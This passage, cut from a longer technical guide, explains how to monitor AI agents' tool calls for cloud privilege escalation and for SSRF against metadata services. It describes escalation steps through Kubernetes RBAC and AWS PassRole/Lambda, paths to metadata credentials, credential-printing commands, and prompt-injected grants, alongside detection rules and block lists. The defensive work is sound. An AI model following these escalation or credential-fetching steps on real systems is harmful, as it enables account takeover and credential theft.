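The verbs `escalate` and `bind` lift these restrictions. Anyone with `escalate` can give a role permissions that they lack themselves, and anyone with `bind` can grant a role stronger than their own. The verb `impersonate` lets its holder act as another user, as `kubectl` does with the option `--as`. A rule should match any new or changed role that contains one of these three verbs or the wildcard `*`, which includes them all.

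The Kubernetes documentation gives an example role, `role-grantor`, that lets user-1 grant other users the admin, edit and view roles in one namespace (a named section of a cluster). The role doesn't restrict who can receive these roles, so user-1 could also grant itself the admin role there. An agent with a role like this can escalate its privileges by creating a single RoleBinding.

A RoleBinding applies in one namespace and a ClusterRoleBinding applies in all of them, so changing `rolebinding` to `clusterrolebinding` in a command can turn access to a test namespace into access to production. A rule should match every new ClusterRoleBinding and assign the highest severity to any that refers to `cluster-admin` or to all service accounts (identities for software in the cluster).

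Several other permissions give more than their names suggest. Kubernetes' *Role Based Access Control Good Practices* lists these among others:

- Anyone who can create pods (running groups of containers) in a namespace can run them as any service account there, and so gains that account's permissions.
- Anyone who can create `serviceaccounts/token` can issue tokens for existing service accounts.
- Anyone who can create and approve certificate requests can make a login certificate in the name of a system component.
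- The verb `get` on `nodes/proxy` lets its holder run commands in every pod on a machine, without passing through the audit log.

Because of the last item, a detector can't assume that every `get` permission allows only harmless reads. Google Cloud's *Best practices for GKE RBAC* also tells customers to watch for `escalate`, `bind` and certificate requests when they design roles for its hosted Kubernetes service.

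### Gaining a role's powers through a new function

Many cloud services need a role to act on a customer's behalf. A user needs the `iam:PassRole` permission to give a service a role. AWS gives the example of Alice, who isn't allowed to perform any operations on S3, its file storage service. If she can pass another service a role that allows S3 operations, that service can perform them for her.

Suppose an agent has the same limits as Alice, but may pass roles and may create and run functions on Lambda, AWS's service for running small programs. The gain takes three steps:

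1. The agent creates a function with code that it wrote, and names a role with full access to S3 in the `--role` argument.
2. AWS checks that the agent may pass this role, then creates the function.
3. The agent runs the function, and the code reads the files under the role's permissions.

These steps don't change any policy in the account, so a rule that only detects policy changes will miss them. Yet the agent can now read files that its own policies don't allow it to read.

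AWS classes Lambda's AddPermission operation as "Permissions management" but CreateFunction only as "Write", so a rule based on these official labels covers the first and misses the second. Searching the logs for PassRole doesn't help either, because PassRole is a permission, not an operation. AWS explains that the passed role appears in the log entry for CreateFunction.

The detector can find the role in the call's arguments, then look up what the role allows. This check also works for other services, since any call that passes a role has to include it somewhere. Calls that change existing resources are harder to check. For example, UpdateFunctionCode replaces the program in a function that already has a role, so its arguments contain the function's name but not the role's. The detector has to query the provider for the function's role.

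### Using a stronger credential that was lying around

Rules that detect permission changes would have missed the token in the PocketOS case, because the hosting provider accepted it without any change to the account. Credentials from the metadata service can also work without a permission change.

Each session should have a list of the credentials and roles it may use. The detector checks the identity behind each call against this list, including any identity specified by a profile, token, header or `--as` option in the call's text. It also has to detect calls to AssumeRole, the AWS operation that exchanges an identity's credentials for a role's. Assuming a role on the list is normal, but assuming any other role should require approval, even if AWS would permit it.

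### How many escalation paths there are

An escalation path is a set of permissions that lets an identity gain another identity's powers or widen its own. In 2018 Spencer Gietzen of Rhino Security Labs, a security testing company, described 21 such paths on AWS. Datadog Security Labs' *Introducing Pathfinding.cloud* (2025) reports that by 2021 a training environment for security testers contained 31 paths, of which four open-source scanners each found between 14 and 22. In December 2025 Datadog, a monitoring company, published a catalogue of 65 paths, of which 27 (42%) went undetected by every open-source tool it evaluated.

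The count has kept growing, and the catalogue's author reported over a dozen new paths in a June 2026 conference talk. *Discovering New AWS Privilege Escalation Paths with an AI-Driven Workflow* (Art, 2026) describes a language model that proposes paths and automated tests that confirm them. Attackers can presumably set up a similar search.

Scanners have improved since then, though it's hard to tell by how much. haitmg.pl's *5 AWS IAM Privesc Scanners vs 57 Paths* (2026) found that coverage ranged from 7% for CloudFox to 93% for cloud-audit. But 25 of the 57 paths came from cloud-audit's own catalogue, a bias disclosed in the article. Of the other 32, Prowler found 31 and cloud-audit found 28. The percentages do show how quickly a list written from one catalogue falls behind, but they don't measure how well a rule recognises a call, because all these scanners look for permissions that identities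 already hold.

Covering all 65 paths also takes fewer than 65 rules, because Datadog Security Labs counts variants separately, such as UpdateFunctionCode with and without permission to run the function. Every path that passes a role to a new resource has the same structure, whether the resource is a virtual machine, a function or a code interpreter for AI agents. A rule that looks for a role in any argument covers all of these paths, including those in services that AWS hasn't launched yet, whereas a rule that lists CreateFunction and RunInstances covers only two services.

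A fixed list also causes false alarms, because most escalation paths work only under particular conditions. For example, an attacker who calls UpdateFunctionCode gains no new permissions if the function has no role, and can't use the role if the function never runs.

### Comparing permissions before and after the call

A sturdier rule uses the list of operations only to decide which calls deserve a closer look. It then works out the effective permissions before and after the call, and bases the verdict on the difference:

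```
id: ESC-GAIN-01
name: An identity gains effective permissions
action_types: [shell_command, api_call, network_request,
               code_execution]
match:
  any:
    - operation_in: permission_operations
    - any_argument_is: role
    - operation_in: code_changes      # e.g. UpdateFunctionCode
    - credential_not_in: session_credentials
severity: high
gain: permissions after the call that were missing before
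verdict:
  no gain: allow
  gain that fits approved_grants: allow
  gain by the agent itself: block
  any other gain: ask
exemptions: none
tags: [T1098.003, T1098.006, AML.T0053]
```

The detector applies the first matching line of the verdict. If it can't compute the gain in permissions, it refers the decision to a person. Blocking changes that give the agent itself more permissions does little harm, because an owner who wants the agent to have them can grant them from their own account.

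AWS offers part of the computation as a service. Its *CheckNoNewAccess* operation compares a new policy with an existing one. It returns PASS if the new policy allows nothing that the existing one doesn't, and FAIL if it might.

Consider a case based on one that AWS uses to explain the check. Dana may start and stop only the virtual machines that carry her name in their `Owner` tag:

```
{
  "Version": "2012-10-17",
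  "Statement": [{
    "Effect": "Allow",
    "Action": ["ec2:StartInstances", "ec2:StopInstances"],
    "Resource": "*",
    "Condition": {"StringEquals":
      {"aws:ResourceTag/Owner": "${aws:username}"}}
  }]
}
```

An agent that helps Dana gets a refusal when it tries to stop a colleague's machine, and proposes a simpler policy:

```
{
  "Version": "2012-10-17",
  "Statement": [{
    "Effect": "Allow",
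    "Action": ["ec2:StartInstances", "ec2:StopInstances"],
    "Resource": "*"
  }]
}
```

Both versions of the policy allow the same two operations, and the new one is shorter, so a rule that looks for added operations finds nothing. But if Dana owns three of the account's 40 machines, the change raises the number of allowed operation-machine pairs from 2 × 3 = 6 to 2 × 40 = 80. CheckNoNewAccess returns FAIL because the new version lacks the condition that limited the operations to Dana's machines. The detector blocks the change if the agent uses Dana's credentials, because the agent itself would gain the 74 additional pairs. If the agent has its own identity, the detector asks for approval instead.

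A full check takes four steps:

1. The detector fetches all the policies that apply to the identity, using its own read-only credentials, and joins them into one document. Otherwise a new policy that repeats an old permission would look like a gain.
2. It makes a second document that includes the proposed change.
3. It sends both to CheckNoNewAccess.
4. If the answer is FAIL, it tests each document for critical operations, such as attaching policies. AWS's *CheckAccessNotGranted* describes a companion operation for this. If only the new document fails, the change adds a critical permission, and the approval prompt should name it.

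The same operation can check a passed role. The detector submits the caller's policies as the old document and the role's policies as the new one, and FAIL means that the role may be able to do something the caller can't. When a change affects who may assume a role, the detector uses the operation to compare the role's old and new trust policies.

In Kubernetes, the comparison needs no paid service. Role rules only add permissions, so the detector can combine the permissions from each binding. The command `kubectl auth reconcile --dry-run=client` shows what a file of role changes would do without applying it. On Google Cloud and Azure, the detector can expand each role into its permissions and compare the sets at each scope, but this requires writing and maintaining more code.

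### What the comparison costs and what it misses

AWS charges about £1.97 for 1,000 policy checks. If an agent makes 10,000 calls a month and 100 of them involve permissions, checking those 100 costs about 20 pence. Each check also adds some delay and needs read access to the account's policies. If the service returns an error or rejects a check because it has received too many requests at once, the detector should refer the call to a person.

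The larger weakness is that the check's result depends only on the policy documents. AWS's *Checks for validating policies* explains that the check doesn't consider the environment, such as which accounts belong to the organisation. If a policy admits everyone in the organisation, it admits more people when a new account joins, even though its text hasn't changed.

Dana's policy has a similar gap. Her access depends on a tag, so an agent that is allowed to edit tags can tag a colleague's machine with her name. She can then stop that machine, even though no policy has changed. To detect this, the detector can list the tags used in policy conditions and treat a change to any of them as a permission change.

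The comparison can also raise needless alarms when a company-wide limit forbids an operation that the new policy allows, because the identity gains nothing in practice. Leaving such limits out of the comparison is still safer, since someone may lift them later without checking every policy they restrict.

Finally, each comparison covers only one call, so a detector may judge the first step in a chain of changes to be minor. Datadog Security Labs' *Pathfinding Labs* (2026) gives the example of an identity that reaches a storage bucket by assuming three roles in a row, where only the last role has access to the bucket. Tools that map the account as a graph of identities can find such chains in advance. Prowler's *Attack Paths* describes one such tool, and Datadog's *AWS IAM role without administrative access has a direct privilege-escalation path* describes a rule that flags any ordinary role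 with a direct path to an administrator. A detector can check the latest scan results and ask for approval before an agent assumes a flagged role.

### An intrusion that reached administrator rights in eight minutes

Brucato and Clark (2026), who work for the cloud security company Sysdig, report in *AI-assisted cloud intrusion achieves admin access in 8 minutes* that an outside attacker broke into a company's AWS account on 28 November 2025 and had administrator rights eight minutes later. The attacker made the calls with stolen keys, not through the victim's AI agents, so a detector attached to those agents would never have received them. However, an agent with the same keys could make the same calls by mistake or through prompt injection.

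The attacker found the keys in public storage buckets. They belonged to a user with read access to most of the account, permission to change Lambda functions and limited access to AWS's AI models. The attacker first tried to assume roles with names like `sysadmin`, but AWS denied the requests. The attacker then replaced the code of an existing function called `EC2-init`, which ran under an administrator role. The new code created an access key for another user and returned it in the function's output. The first target, `adminGH`, had no administrator rights despite its name. After two more versions of the code, the attacker had a key for a user with administrator rights.

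Brucato and Clark infer that a language model helped the attacker. The attacker's code had thorough error handling and appeared very quickly. They also tried account numbers that didn't belong to the company, such as 123456789012, referred to a GitHub repository that doesn't exist, and named one session "claude-session". The evidence is circumstantial but fairly persuasive.

| Step | List of policy changes | Before-and-after comparison |
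|---|---|---|
| Using keys from a public bucket | Misses it | Misses it, because the keys are valid and nothing changes |
| Trying to assume administrator roles | Misses it | Catches it, because the roles are stronger and not on the session's list |
| Replacing the code of `EC2-init` | Misses it | Catches it, because the function's role is stronger than the user |
| Creating a key for an administrator | Catches it in the logs | Catches it in the logs |
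| Attaching an administrator policy to a new user | Catches it | Catches it, but the attacker is already an administrator |

The function itself created the key, so a rule on tool calls could have detected this step only by finding the operation's name in the uploaded code, as with any script the agent writes. A log rule would have detected the operation after it ran, when the attacker already had the key.

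That makes the code replacement the best place to stop the attack. Brucato and Clark list a Sysdig rule for this operation, and others for new access keys and administrator policies. They don't report whether the victim used any of them. A rule that fires on every code change would also fire on ordinary deployments, so a busy team might well have ignored it. The comparison singles out this change because the function's role had administrator rights that the user's policies didn't grant.

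Later, the attacker took over more identities. Sysdig's count of 19 combines five users with 14 sessions under six roles. The attacker created new keys for four existing users, and the fifth user, `backdoor-admin`, was new.

### False alarms from ordinary infrastructure work

Setting up infrastructure often involves legitimate gains in permissions. AWS notes that applications typically run with different permissions from the developer who creates them. Under the definition at the start of this section, a developer's agent therefore escalates its privileges almost every time it deploys a function, so ESC-GAIN-01 would block work that the team wants done.

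The detector checks role assignments against the list `approved_grants`. Each entry names a function or service, the role it runs under, and the identities that may deploy it. For example, the detector allows the agent to update `resize-images` if the update keeps that function's usual role. The entries should name exact roles, because AWS warns that tagging roles to control who may pass them doesn't work reliably.

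An approved entry must never include a role with critical permissions. In the Sysdig case, the user probably existed to automate work with Lambda, so a team listing its usual deployments might have approved `EC2-init` with its administrator role. The detector would then have allowed the attack. The detector should look up the role's current permissions at each deployment, because someone may have added permissions to the role after the entry was approved.

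A new role needs a different comparison, because it starts with no permissions and everything it receives would count as a gain. The team can write a reference policy for each common kind of service, such as one that may read a single bucket and write logs. CheckNoNewAccess then compares the new role's policy with the reference policy, and the detector allows the role if the result is PASS. A person has to review only the roles that exceed their reference policy.

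For infrastructure as code, the detector can take all the changes to roles and policies from the saved Terraform plan and put them in one approval prompt. People who had to answer ten separate prompts about one deployment would learn to click "yes". The plan may also contain a role that does no harm yet but creates a path to privilege escalation. Datadog's *Role with privilege escalation by actions 'lambda:CreateFunction' and 'iam:PassRole' and 'lambda:InvokeFunction'* describes a rule that finds one such combination of permissions in Terraform code. The remedy is usually a small change that limits the role to passing one named role instead of any role.

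### When a grant to someone else should raise an alarm

Agents also grant permissions to other people and programs, often at the user's request. Kubernetes' built-in condition makes a good first test. A grant is suspicious if it would give the recipient a permission that the agent doesn't have. But many agents run with a developer's administrator keys and already have every permission, so this test never raises an alarm. Because these agents can't gain permissions themselves, the only escalation left to detect is their grants to others.

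The detector therefore needs tests that don't depend on the agent's own power:

| Recipient or permission | Verdict | Reason |
|---|---|---|
| An identity that the agent can use, such as a role it may assume | Block | The agent gains the permission itself |
| An account outside the company | Block, unless a person has listed it | Nobody in the company controls what happens there |
| Everyone, or all service accounts in a cluster | Block | Any compromised program could use the grant |
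| A critical permission for anyone | Ask | The recipient could go on to grant more |
| A colleague whom the user named, with ordinary permissions | Allow, with a log entry | The user requested it |
| A colleague whom the user didn't name | Ask | The name may come from a planted instruction |

An agent with administrator keys may be able to assume almost any role, so for that agent the first row should cover only the roles on its session's list. As with email addresses, the detector must take the colleague's name from the user's own messages. It should also check that the permission matches the request. If the user asks the agent to let Sam read the sales reports and the agent proposes a policy with `s3:*` on every bucket, the policy gives access to the right person but would also let Sam delete the files.

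## Detecting requests to cloud metadata addresses

An agent on a cloud machine can often gain permissions with one or two web requests to the metadata service, without changing a policy or finding a key in a file. The agent rarely has a good reason to read the machine's credentials directly, so a request for them is usually easy to judge, but it is harder to work out where a request will go.

### How a machine gets its credentials

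On AWS, the original method takes four steps:

1. An administrator attaches a role to the machine.
2. A program on the machine sends a GET request, the kind a browser uses to load a page, to `http://169.254.169.254/latest/meta-data/iam/security-credentials/` followed by the role's name.
3. The service returns an access key, a secret key, a session token and an expiry time.
4. The program signs its requests to AWS with these values, and AWS applies the role's permissions.

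AWS's *Retrieve security credentials from instance metadata* explains that AWS offers new credentials at least five minutes before the old ones expire. Credentials work outside the machine until they expire, so anyone who sees them in a tool's output can use them. The same page warns customers about services that make web requests on someone's behalf, such as proxies and HTML validators. An agent's fetch tool also makes requests this way.

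In 2019 AWS added a second version of the service, which requires an extra request. According to AWS's *How Instance Metadata Service Version 2 works*, the program first sends a PUT request, a type normally used to upload data. A header in this request states how long the session should last, from one second to six hours. The service returns a session token, which the program must include in every later GET request. The token works only on the machine that requested it. The service rejects PUT requests that contain an `X-Forwarded-For` header, because proxies add this header to record the original caller.

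Version 2 also limits how far the token can travel. Every device that forwards a network packet lowers a counter in the packet by one and discards the packet if the counter reaches zero. The counter in the reply that contains the token starts at 1 by default, so the reply can reach programs on the machine but can't be forwarded any further. A container with its own network usually adds a forwarding step, so AWS's *IMDSv2* sets the default limit to 2 for its Amazon Linux 2023 images. An agent in a container on such a machine can therefore probably get a token as easily as a program outside the container.

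Google Cloud and Azure each use one GET request with a fixed header. Google Cloud's *View and query VM metadata* requires `Metadata-Flavor: Google`. The server returns an access token that covers everything the administrator allowed when setting up the machine, unless the caller asks for less. Microsoft's *Azure Instance Metadata Service* requires `Metadata: true` and rejects any request with an `X-Forwarded-For` header. The caller also names the cloud service it wants to use, such as file storage. According to Entra Diff's *How Managed Identities Work Vm* (2026), which tracks changes in Microsoft's documentation, Azure then requests a token for that service from Entra ID, Microsoft's identity system, using a certificate that belongs to the machine's identity.

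These requirements matter when an outsider can influence a request but can't write all of it. The table assumes that the machine has a role and that the outsider sees the reply.

| The outsider controls | AWS version 1 | AWS version 2 | Google Cloud | Azure |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| The address | Gets credentials | Refused | Refused | Refused |
| The address and headers | Gets credentials | Refused | Gets credentials | Gets credentials |
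| The address, headers and method (GET or PUT) | Gets credentials | Gets credentials | Gets credentials | Gets credentials |

AWS gave this reasoning when it introduced version 2 in *Add defense in depth against open firewalls, reverse proxies, and SSRF vulnerabilities*. The company reports finding many flaws that let an attacker set arbitrary headers, so requiring a fixed header would not stop the attacker. It claims that requiring a PUT request and a secret token protects against the "vast majority" of real SSRF flaws, but gives no count.

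Version 2 protects a machine only if version 1 is off. According to AWS's *Configure the Instance Metadata Service options*, a new machine accepts both versions unless its launch settings, the account's default or the machine image requires version 2.

### A shell command and a fetch tool need different checks

People use the term SSRF for two situations that need different defences. In one, the agent runs `curl` in its own shell to request its machine's credentials, without tricking a server into making the request. The shell can send any header and use any method, so it matches the bottom row of the table, and none of the providers' requirements stop it. Microsoft says its metadata service is open to every process on the machine. The detector has to catch the command before it runs, with a block on the network route as a backup.

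In the other situation, which is SSRF proper, the agent passes an address to a fetch tool and an MCP server makes the request. The address 169.254.169.254 always reaches the metadata service of the machine that sends the request, so the credentials at risk are those of the server's machine. An agent on a laptop, which has no metadata service, can still obtain the credentials of a fetch tool that runs in the cloud.

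A hook on the agent's side can read the URL in the tool call, but the MCP server resolves the hostname, follows redirects and opens the connection. The server may also be on a network where the same hostname resolves to a different IP address. The full check therefore has to run inside the server. A team that uses someone else's fetch tool can check only the URL that its agent sends, and has to rely on the server's operator to check the resolved IP address and any redirects.

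In January 2026 the security company BlueRock disclosed that the MCP server for Microsoft's MarkItDown, which converts documents to a simple text format, would fetch any address without checking it. Petri's *Critical MCP Server Flaws Turn AI Assistants Into Gateways* reports that an attacker could use it to extract AWS credentials if the server ran on an AWS machine with version 1 of the metadata service. Version 2 would probably have refused the request, because the server's tool takes only an address. The tool could also read the server's local files through addresses beginning with `file://`, according to *Otto Support*, a review of several such flaws by the security testing company Bishop Fox.

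Microsoft replied that the scenario created no significant risk, because a user would have to deliberately use the feature in a way its designers hadn't intended. It also rejected another company's report about MarkItDown as "working as intended", according to OX Security's *MCP Security Alert*. Microsoft's reasoning holds only if the user chooses the address, but a web page or document can supply it through prompt injection. According to Bishop Fox, the recommended fix is to accept connections only from the same machine. This blocks connections from other machines, but an agent on the same machine can still call the tool with a planted address.

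### Grafana: when version 2 isn't enough

Grafana makes monitoring dashboards, and its MCP server lets agents query them. SC Media reports that the security company Pillar Security found a flaw in this server, CVE-2026-19516, with a severity of 9.1 out of 10. A caller could put another host's address in the `X-Grafana-URL` header and choose the request's method, path and body. The server's `grafana_api_request` tool then sent the request to that host and returned the reply.

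In Pillar's tests, researchers used this to complete AWS's version 2 exchange. They sent the PUT request with its lifetime header, received a session token, and used the token in another request to fetch the credentials. The caller must also have been able to set headers, because both requests need them. Version 2 worked as designed, but it couldn't distinguish the Grafana server from a legitimate program on the same machine.

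Ariel Fogel of Pillar cautions that not every Grafana MCP server could reach a metadata service. The server has to run on a cloud machine with a role, and in a container the hop limit might still stop the token from arriving. Grafana fixed the flaw in version 1.1.0. That version also added optional access tokens, because the server had accepted calls from anyone who made up a session identifier in the right format.

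The destination wasn't in the tool's arguments, so a detection hook that read them would have found a tool name and an API path, but no foreign host. Bishop Fox describes the same design in mcp-atlassian, a server for Atlassian's project-management software with over 4 million downloads, where the headers `X-Atlassian-Jira-Url` and `X-Atlassian-Confluence-Url` set the destination. Version 0.17.0 added a list of permitted domains. A server that talks to one known service should take the destination from the operator's configuration and ignore any address from the caller.

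### Which addresses belong on the list

A rule that blocks all addresses beginning with 169.254 (169.254.0.0/16) covers the usual metadata address at all three large providers, but not every way to reach their metadata services.

| Service | Address | Inside 169.254.0.0/16? |
|---|---|---|
| AWS, Google Cloud and Azure machines | 169.254.169.254 | Yes |
| AWS over IPv6, if someone has enabled it | fd00:ec2::254 | No |
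| Google Cloud machines that have only IPv6 | fd20:ce::254 | No |
| Azure, by an unofficial route | 168.63.129.16 | No |
| Azure App Service | 169.254.129.2 to 169.254.129.4, in one user's report | Yes |

The two entries in IPv6, the newer system of longer internet addresses, fall in fc00::/7, a range for private networks. Published lists of blocked ranges can easily omit it. *Security Considerations for Model Context Protocol (MCP) Implementations in AI Agent Systems* (Syed, 2026) names private IPv4 ranges, a machine's loopback addresses, 169.254.0.0/16 and fe80::/10, and refers to the rest only as "other non-routable ranges". A developer who blocked only the named ranges would leave both IPv6 metadata addresses open. The paper is one person's draft for the internet's standards body, not a standard.

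The unofficial Azure address is harder to cover because it looks like an ordinary public address, so rules that block private ranges miss it. *Azure IMDS (Instance Metadata Service) calls to 168.63.129.16 blocked*, a post by Microsoft employee MinnieLahoti (2024), announced that Azure would permanently refuse metadata requests there after 1 July 2025. Fetch tools should still block the address because they never need to contact it. Blocking it for the whole machine is riskier because Azure also uses it for other communication with the machine.

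Azure App Service, which runs web applications without giving the customer a whole machine, has its own credential service. Tenable's *The Azure Metadata Protection You Didn’t Know Was There* explains that the credential service's address is in the environment variable `IDENTITY_ENDPOINT` and that each request must contain a secret from `IDENTITY_HEADER`. An outsider who controls only the address a request goes to can't supply that secret, but an agent's shell can read both variables. A rule that checks only for 169.254.169.254 would miss the addresses in the table's last row, which come from Keene (2025), *Occasionally receiving errored request from Managed Identity end points to receive token*. The detector can read `IDENTITY_ENDPOINT` at startup, add the address to its list and treat the secret as a credential.

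The list also needs the hostnames of Google's metadata service, `metadata.google.internal` and `metadata.goog`, because a hook running outside Google Cloud may be unable to look up their addresses. Teams that use other providers, such as Alibaba Cloud or Oracle, have to add the addresses given in those providers' documentation.

### The order of checks in a fetch tool

The order of the checks matters because each depends on the result of the one before. Bishop Fox and Syed recommend much the same order.

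1. **Parse the address.** An IP address has several valid spellings. For example, software may accept an IPv4 address as one large number, so comparing text with `169.254.169.254` can miss it. A parser converts every spelling to one form. It should be the parser that the request itself will use, because two parsers may disagree about which part of a web address is the host. The tool should also reject everything except `http` and `https`, which would have stopped MarkItDown from reading local files.
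2. **Resolve the name.** The tool looks up all of the host's IPv4 and IPv6 addresses. This catches an innocent-looking name that points to a metadata service.
3. **Compare every address with the blocked ranges.** A name can have several addresses, and a program may try the next one if a connection fails. A single blocked address is therefore enough to refuse the request.
4. **Connect to an address that passed.** Many web libraries look the name up again when they connect. The domain's owner can return a public address for the check and a metadata address a moment later, a trick called DNS rebinding. Connecting directly to the checked address prevents it.
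5. **Repeat all the steps for each redirect.** A permitted site can answer with an instruction to fetch another address, which may be a metadata service.

In outline, the code looks like this:

```
fetch(url, redirects_left = 5):
    u = parse(url)
    refuse unless u.scheme is http or https
    addresses = resolve_all(u.host)
    refuse if addresses is empty
    for a in addresses:
        a = plain_ipv4(a) if a is IPv4-mapped
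        refuse unless is_public(a)
        refuse if a in metadata_addresses
    reply = connect(to = addresses[0], host = u.host,
                    follow_redirects = no)
    if reply is a redirect:
        refuse if redirects_left is 0
        return fetch(reply.location, redirects_left - 1)
    return reply
```

The connection still uses the original host name to check the site's certificate. The function requires a public address instead of listing private ranges, so no one has to remember to list ranges such as fc00::/7. The separate list is still needed for exceptions such as Azure's unofficial address.

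The MCP server auth-fetch-mcp shows why the third step needs a conversion. GitLab's *Advisories for Npm/Auth-Fetch-Mcp package* (2026) lists two flaws in it. The earlier flaw was that the server checked no addresses, so on a cloud machine its `auth_fetch` tool could return credentials in its response, and its `download_media` tool could save them to disk.

Version 3.0.1 checked for private addresses but missed IPv4-mapped addresses, which represent IPv4 addresses in IPv6 form. The server's URL parser rewrote the IPv4 part from the usual four decimal numbers into hexadecimal. The check matched only the decimal form, so it let the request through. GitLab's example is a loopback address, but other blocked IPv4 addresses would presumably have passed in the same way. The remedy is to convert mapped addresses back to IPv4 and compare them as numbers, preferably with a maintained address library.

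The fifth step is also easy to forget. Bishop Fox describes CVE-2026-41297, a flaw in the agent program OpenClaw that let its plugin downloader follow redirects to internal servers without checking them. Syed advises against following redirects by default. That is safest for tools that call an API, but a general web reader that doesn't follow redirects would fail on many ordinary sites.

If the tool needs only a few sites, a list of permitted domains is stronger than a list of blocked addresses. The address checks are still needed, because a permitted site can redirect elsewhere and someone may change the address its domain name resolves to.

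If the fetch tool sends its traffic through a proxy, the proxy resolves the name and opens the connection, so steps 2 to 4 have to run there. The tool should also set the method and headers itself. It can add an `X-Forwarded-For` header to every request, since AWS's version 2 won't issue a token to a request with that header and Azure rejects any request that has it. This takes almost no work, but it doesn't protect a machine that accepts AWS's version 1.

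### A rule for the agent's own calls

The hook on the agent's side needs a simpler rule:

```
id: META-CRED-01
name: Request to a cloud metadata service
action_types: [shell_command, api_call, network_request,
               code_execution]
match:
  any:
    - destination_ip_in: metadata_addresses
    - destination_host_in: metadata_names
    - command_in: credential_printers
severity: critical
verdict:
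  GET from the agent's own shell to harmless_paths: allow
  command in credential_printers: ask
  anything else: block
exemptions: none
tags: [T1552.005, AML.T0055]
```

The list `credential_printers` contains ordinary commands that display the current credentials, such as `aws configure export-credentials`, `gcloud auth print-access-token` and `az account get-access-token`. On a cloud machine, these can return the same secrets as a metadata request, even though they contain no metadata address. The commands also have legitimate uses, such as logging in to a container registry, so the detector asks for confirmation.

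The list `harmless_paths` is for facts such as the machine's region. Entries must match the whole path and any options after it, because Google's service accepts a `recursive=true` option that returns everything below a directory, including custom values a team may have stored there. On an AWS machine that requires version 2, even reading the region takes a session token, and the same token gives access to the credentials. The rule therefore blocks the PUT request for that token, even when the agent only wants harmless facts. A team can avoid this problem by putting the region and machine identifier in environment variables when the session starts.

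When a shell command contains a host name, the detector resolves the name and compares the resulting address with its list. The detector can't make the connection for the shell, so the name may resolve to a different address by the time `curl` connects, and `curl` may follow a redirect that the detector doesn't check. A script can also build the address as it runs. In these cases, only a control on the network route or a machine role with few permissions limits the damage.

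### Does a slow reply prove that credentials were reachable?

For *Exposed by Design*, Padilla (2026) searched the internet for MCP servers in July 2026 and tested 414 of them. One was epwforge, a document-processing server whose `fetch_url` tool accepted any address. When Padilla gave it the AWS metadata address, the reply took 11.9 seconds, compared with a baseline of 0.3 seconds. Padilla concludes that the server could reach the metadata service and, "by implication, that cloud credentials are accessible".

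The delay is weak evidence for that conclusion. A metadata service runs next to the machine and normally replies quickly. According to AWS's *Amazon EC2 instance metadata*, its libraries by default wait one second and try once before giving up. A delay of 11.9 seconds looks more like a connection that failed after several attempts. In *CONTAP-356410*, a support note from the storage company NetApp, a connection to Azure's metadata address took about 75 seconds to fail.

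The baseline is also unclear, because Padilla describes it both as requests to addresses that lead nowhere and as "benign requests". If unreachable addresses failed in 0.3 seconds, the longer delay suggests that the server at least tried to connect to the metadata address. If the baseline was ordinary web pages, any unresponsive address might have caused the same delay. Padilla's test accepts a difference of more than five seconds as confirmation of SSRF. The paper gives the epwforge result as an example of how that threshold was calibrated, so the result isn't independent evidence that the threshold works.

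Even a quick reply wouldn't have shown that credentials were available. The machine also needs a role, and it would probably have to accept version 1 of AWS's metadata service, because the paper describes a tool that takes only an address. Padilla retrieved no metadata, for ethical reasons. Requesting a harmless field, such as the machine's image ID, would have exposed no secrets and shown whether the service was reachable. The paper's method counts this as confirmation. Comparing the result with that of an unused address in the same range would also have helped. Still, the tool accepted any address, which is a flaw whether or not credentials were available, and the list of permitted domains that fixed it was worth adding.

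### What the figures of 30% and 37% count

Articles on MCP security often state that about a third of servers are vulnerable to SSRF. One source for this figure is Equixly (2025), a security company that tested some of the most popular MCP servers over a month and found that 30% "permitted unrestricted URL fetching". Akamai repeats this as 30% "vulnerable to SSRF". The difference matters because a fetch tool on a laptop may accept any address but have no metadata service to expose.

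The higher figure, 36.7%, comes from BlueRock's scan of more than 7,000 servers. OpenClaw AI reports it as the share that is "potentially vulnerable", but the headline of Security Horror's *OLD BUG, NEW DELIVERY* (2026) omits "potentially". Security Horror also describes the servers as publicly exposed, which OpenClaw AI does not. Bishop Fox writes of SSRF across 2,500 MCP servers, probably referring to the same result, since 36.7% of 7,000 is about 2,570.

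| Study | What it examined | What it counted | Share |
|---|---|---|---|
| Equixly | Popular MCP servers | Fetching without restrictions | 30% |
| BlueRock | More than 7,000 MCP servers | Potential SSRF | 36.7% |
| Padilla | 414 servers on the internet | SSRF flagged by an automated test | 7% (29 servers) |

Padilla's lower share doesn't refute the others, because it covers all kinds of servers reachable over the internet, including those with no fetch tool, and the paper doesn't report how often the automated test was wrong. Flagged flaws may be much more common than exploitable ones. Oliveira and Fiser, in *Hunt Them All*, analysed over 19,000 open-source MCP server repositories for the security company Trend Micro and judged only 4.1% of the vulnerabilities identified by AI to be exploitable. Their figure includes every type of flaw, so it can't be used to correct the SSRF percentages,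 but it suggests that many servers counted as "potentially" vulnerable may not be exploitable.

These figures don't measure what share of servers would give cloud credentials to a caller. A team learns more by listing its own fetch tools and the machines they run on, along with each machine's roles and whether it still accepts version 1 requests to AWS's metadata service.

### False alarms from cloud libraries

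Programs constantly fetch credentials from the metadata service, as it was designed to allow. An agent on an AWS machine may run `aws s3 ls`, which contains no metadata address, and the program can fetch the credentials in the background, as AWS's *Use credentials for Amazon EC2 instance metadata* explains. META-CRED-01 doesn't match this call, and shouldn't, because the agent never sees the credentials. The detector still needs to check which role the command will use, as ESC-GAIN-01 does with its list of session credentials.

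A network monitor on the same machine records these background requests and may raise an alarm for each one. According to AWS's *IMDS credential provider*, an AWS library tries the metadata service by default if it finds no valid credentials in several other sources. A developer whose login has expired can therefore trigger an alarm by running an ordinary script, even on a laptop.

The team can reduce this noise by giving the agent's session its own credentials and setting the environment variable `AWS_EC2_METADATA_DISABLED` to `true`. AWS's tools then stop contacting the service, and any remaining request from the session deserves attention. The setting doesn't stop `curl` or other programs from contacting the service, and it breaks any script that depends on the machine's role. An agent can also unset the variable, so the detector should flag commands that change it.

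META-CRED-01 checks only the destination of a request, so it allows an agent to write a firewall rule that blocks 169.254.169.254. A rule that searched the text of tool calls for that address would stop the agent from doing so. Setup scripts that read the machine's region are harder to handle, because the same script may also read credentials. The detector should examine each request in the script separately, and block the script if it can't determine every destination.

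## Detecting harm spread over several calls

An attacker who fetches a credential from the metadata service needs further calls to use it. Those calls can look like ordinary data work, and a rule that checks one call at a time can't connect them to the fetch.

### One attack across three classes

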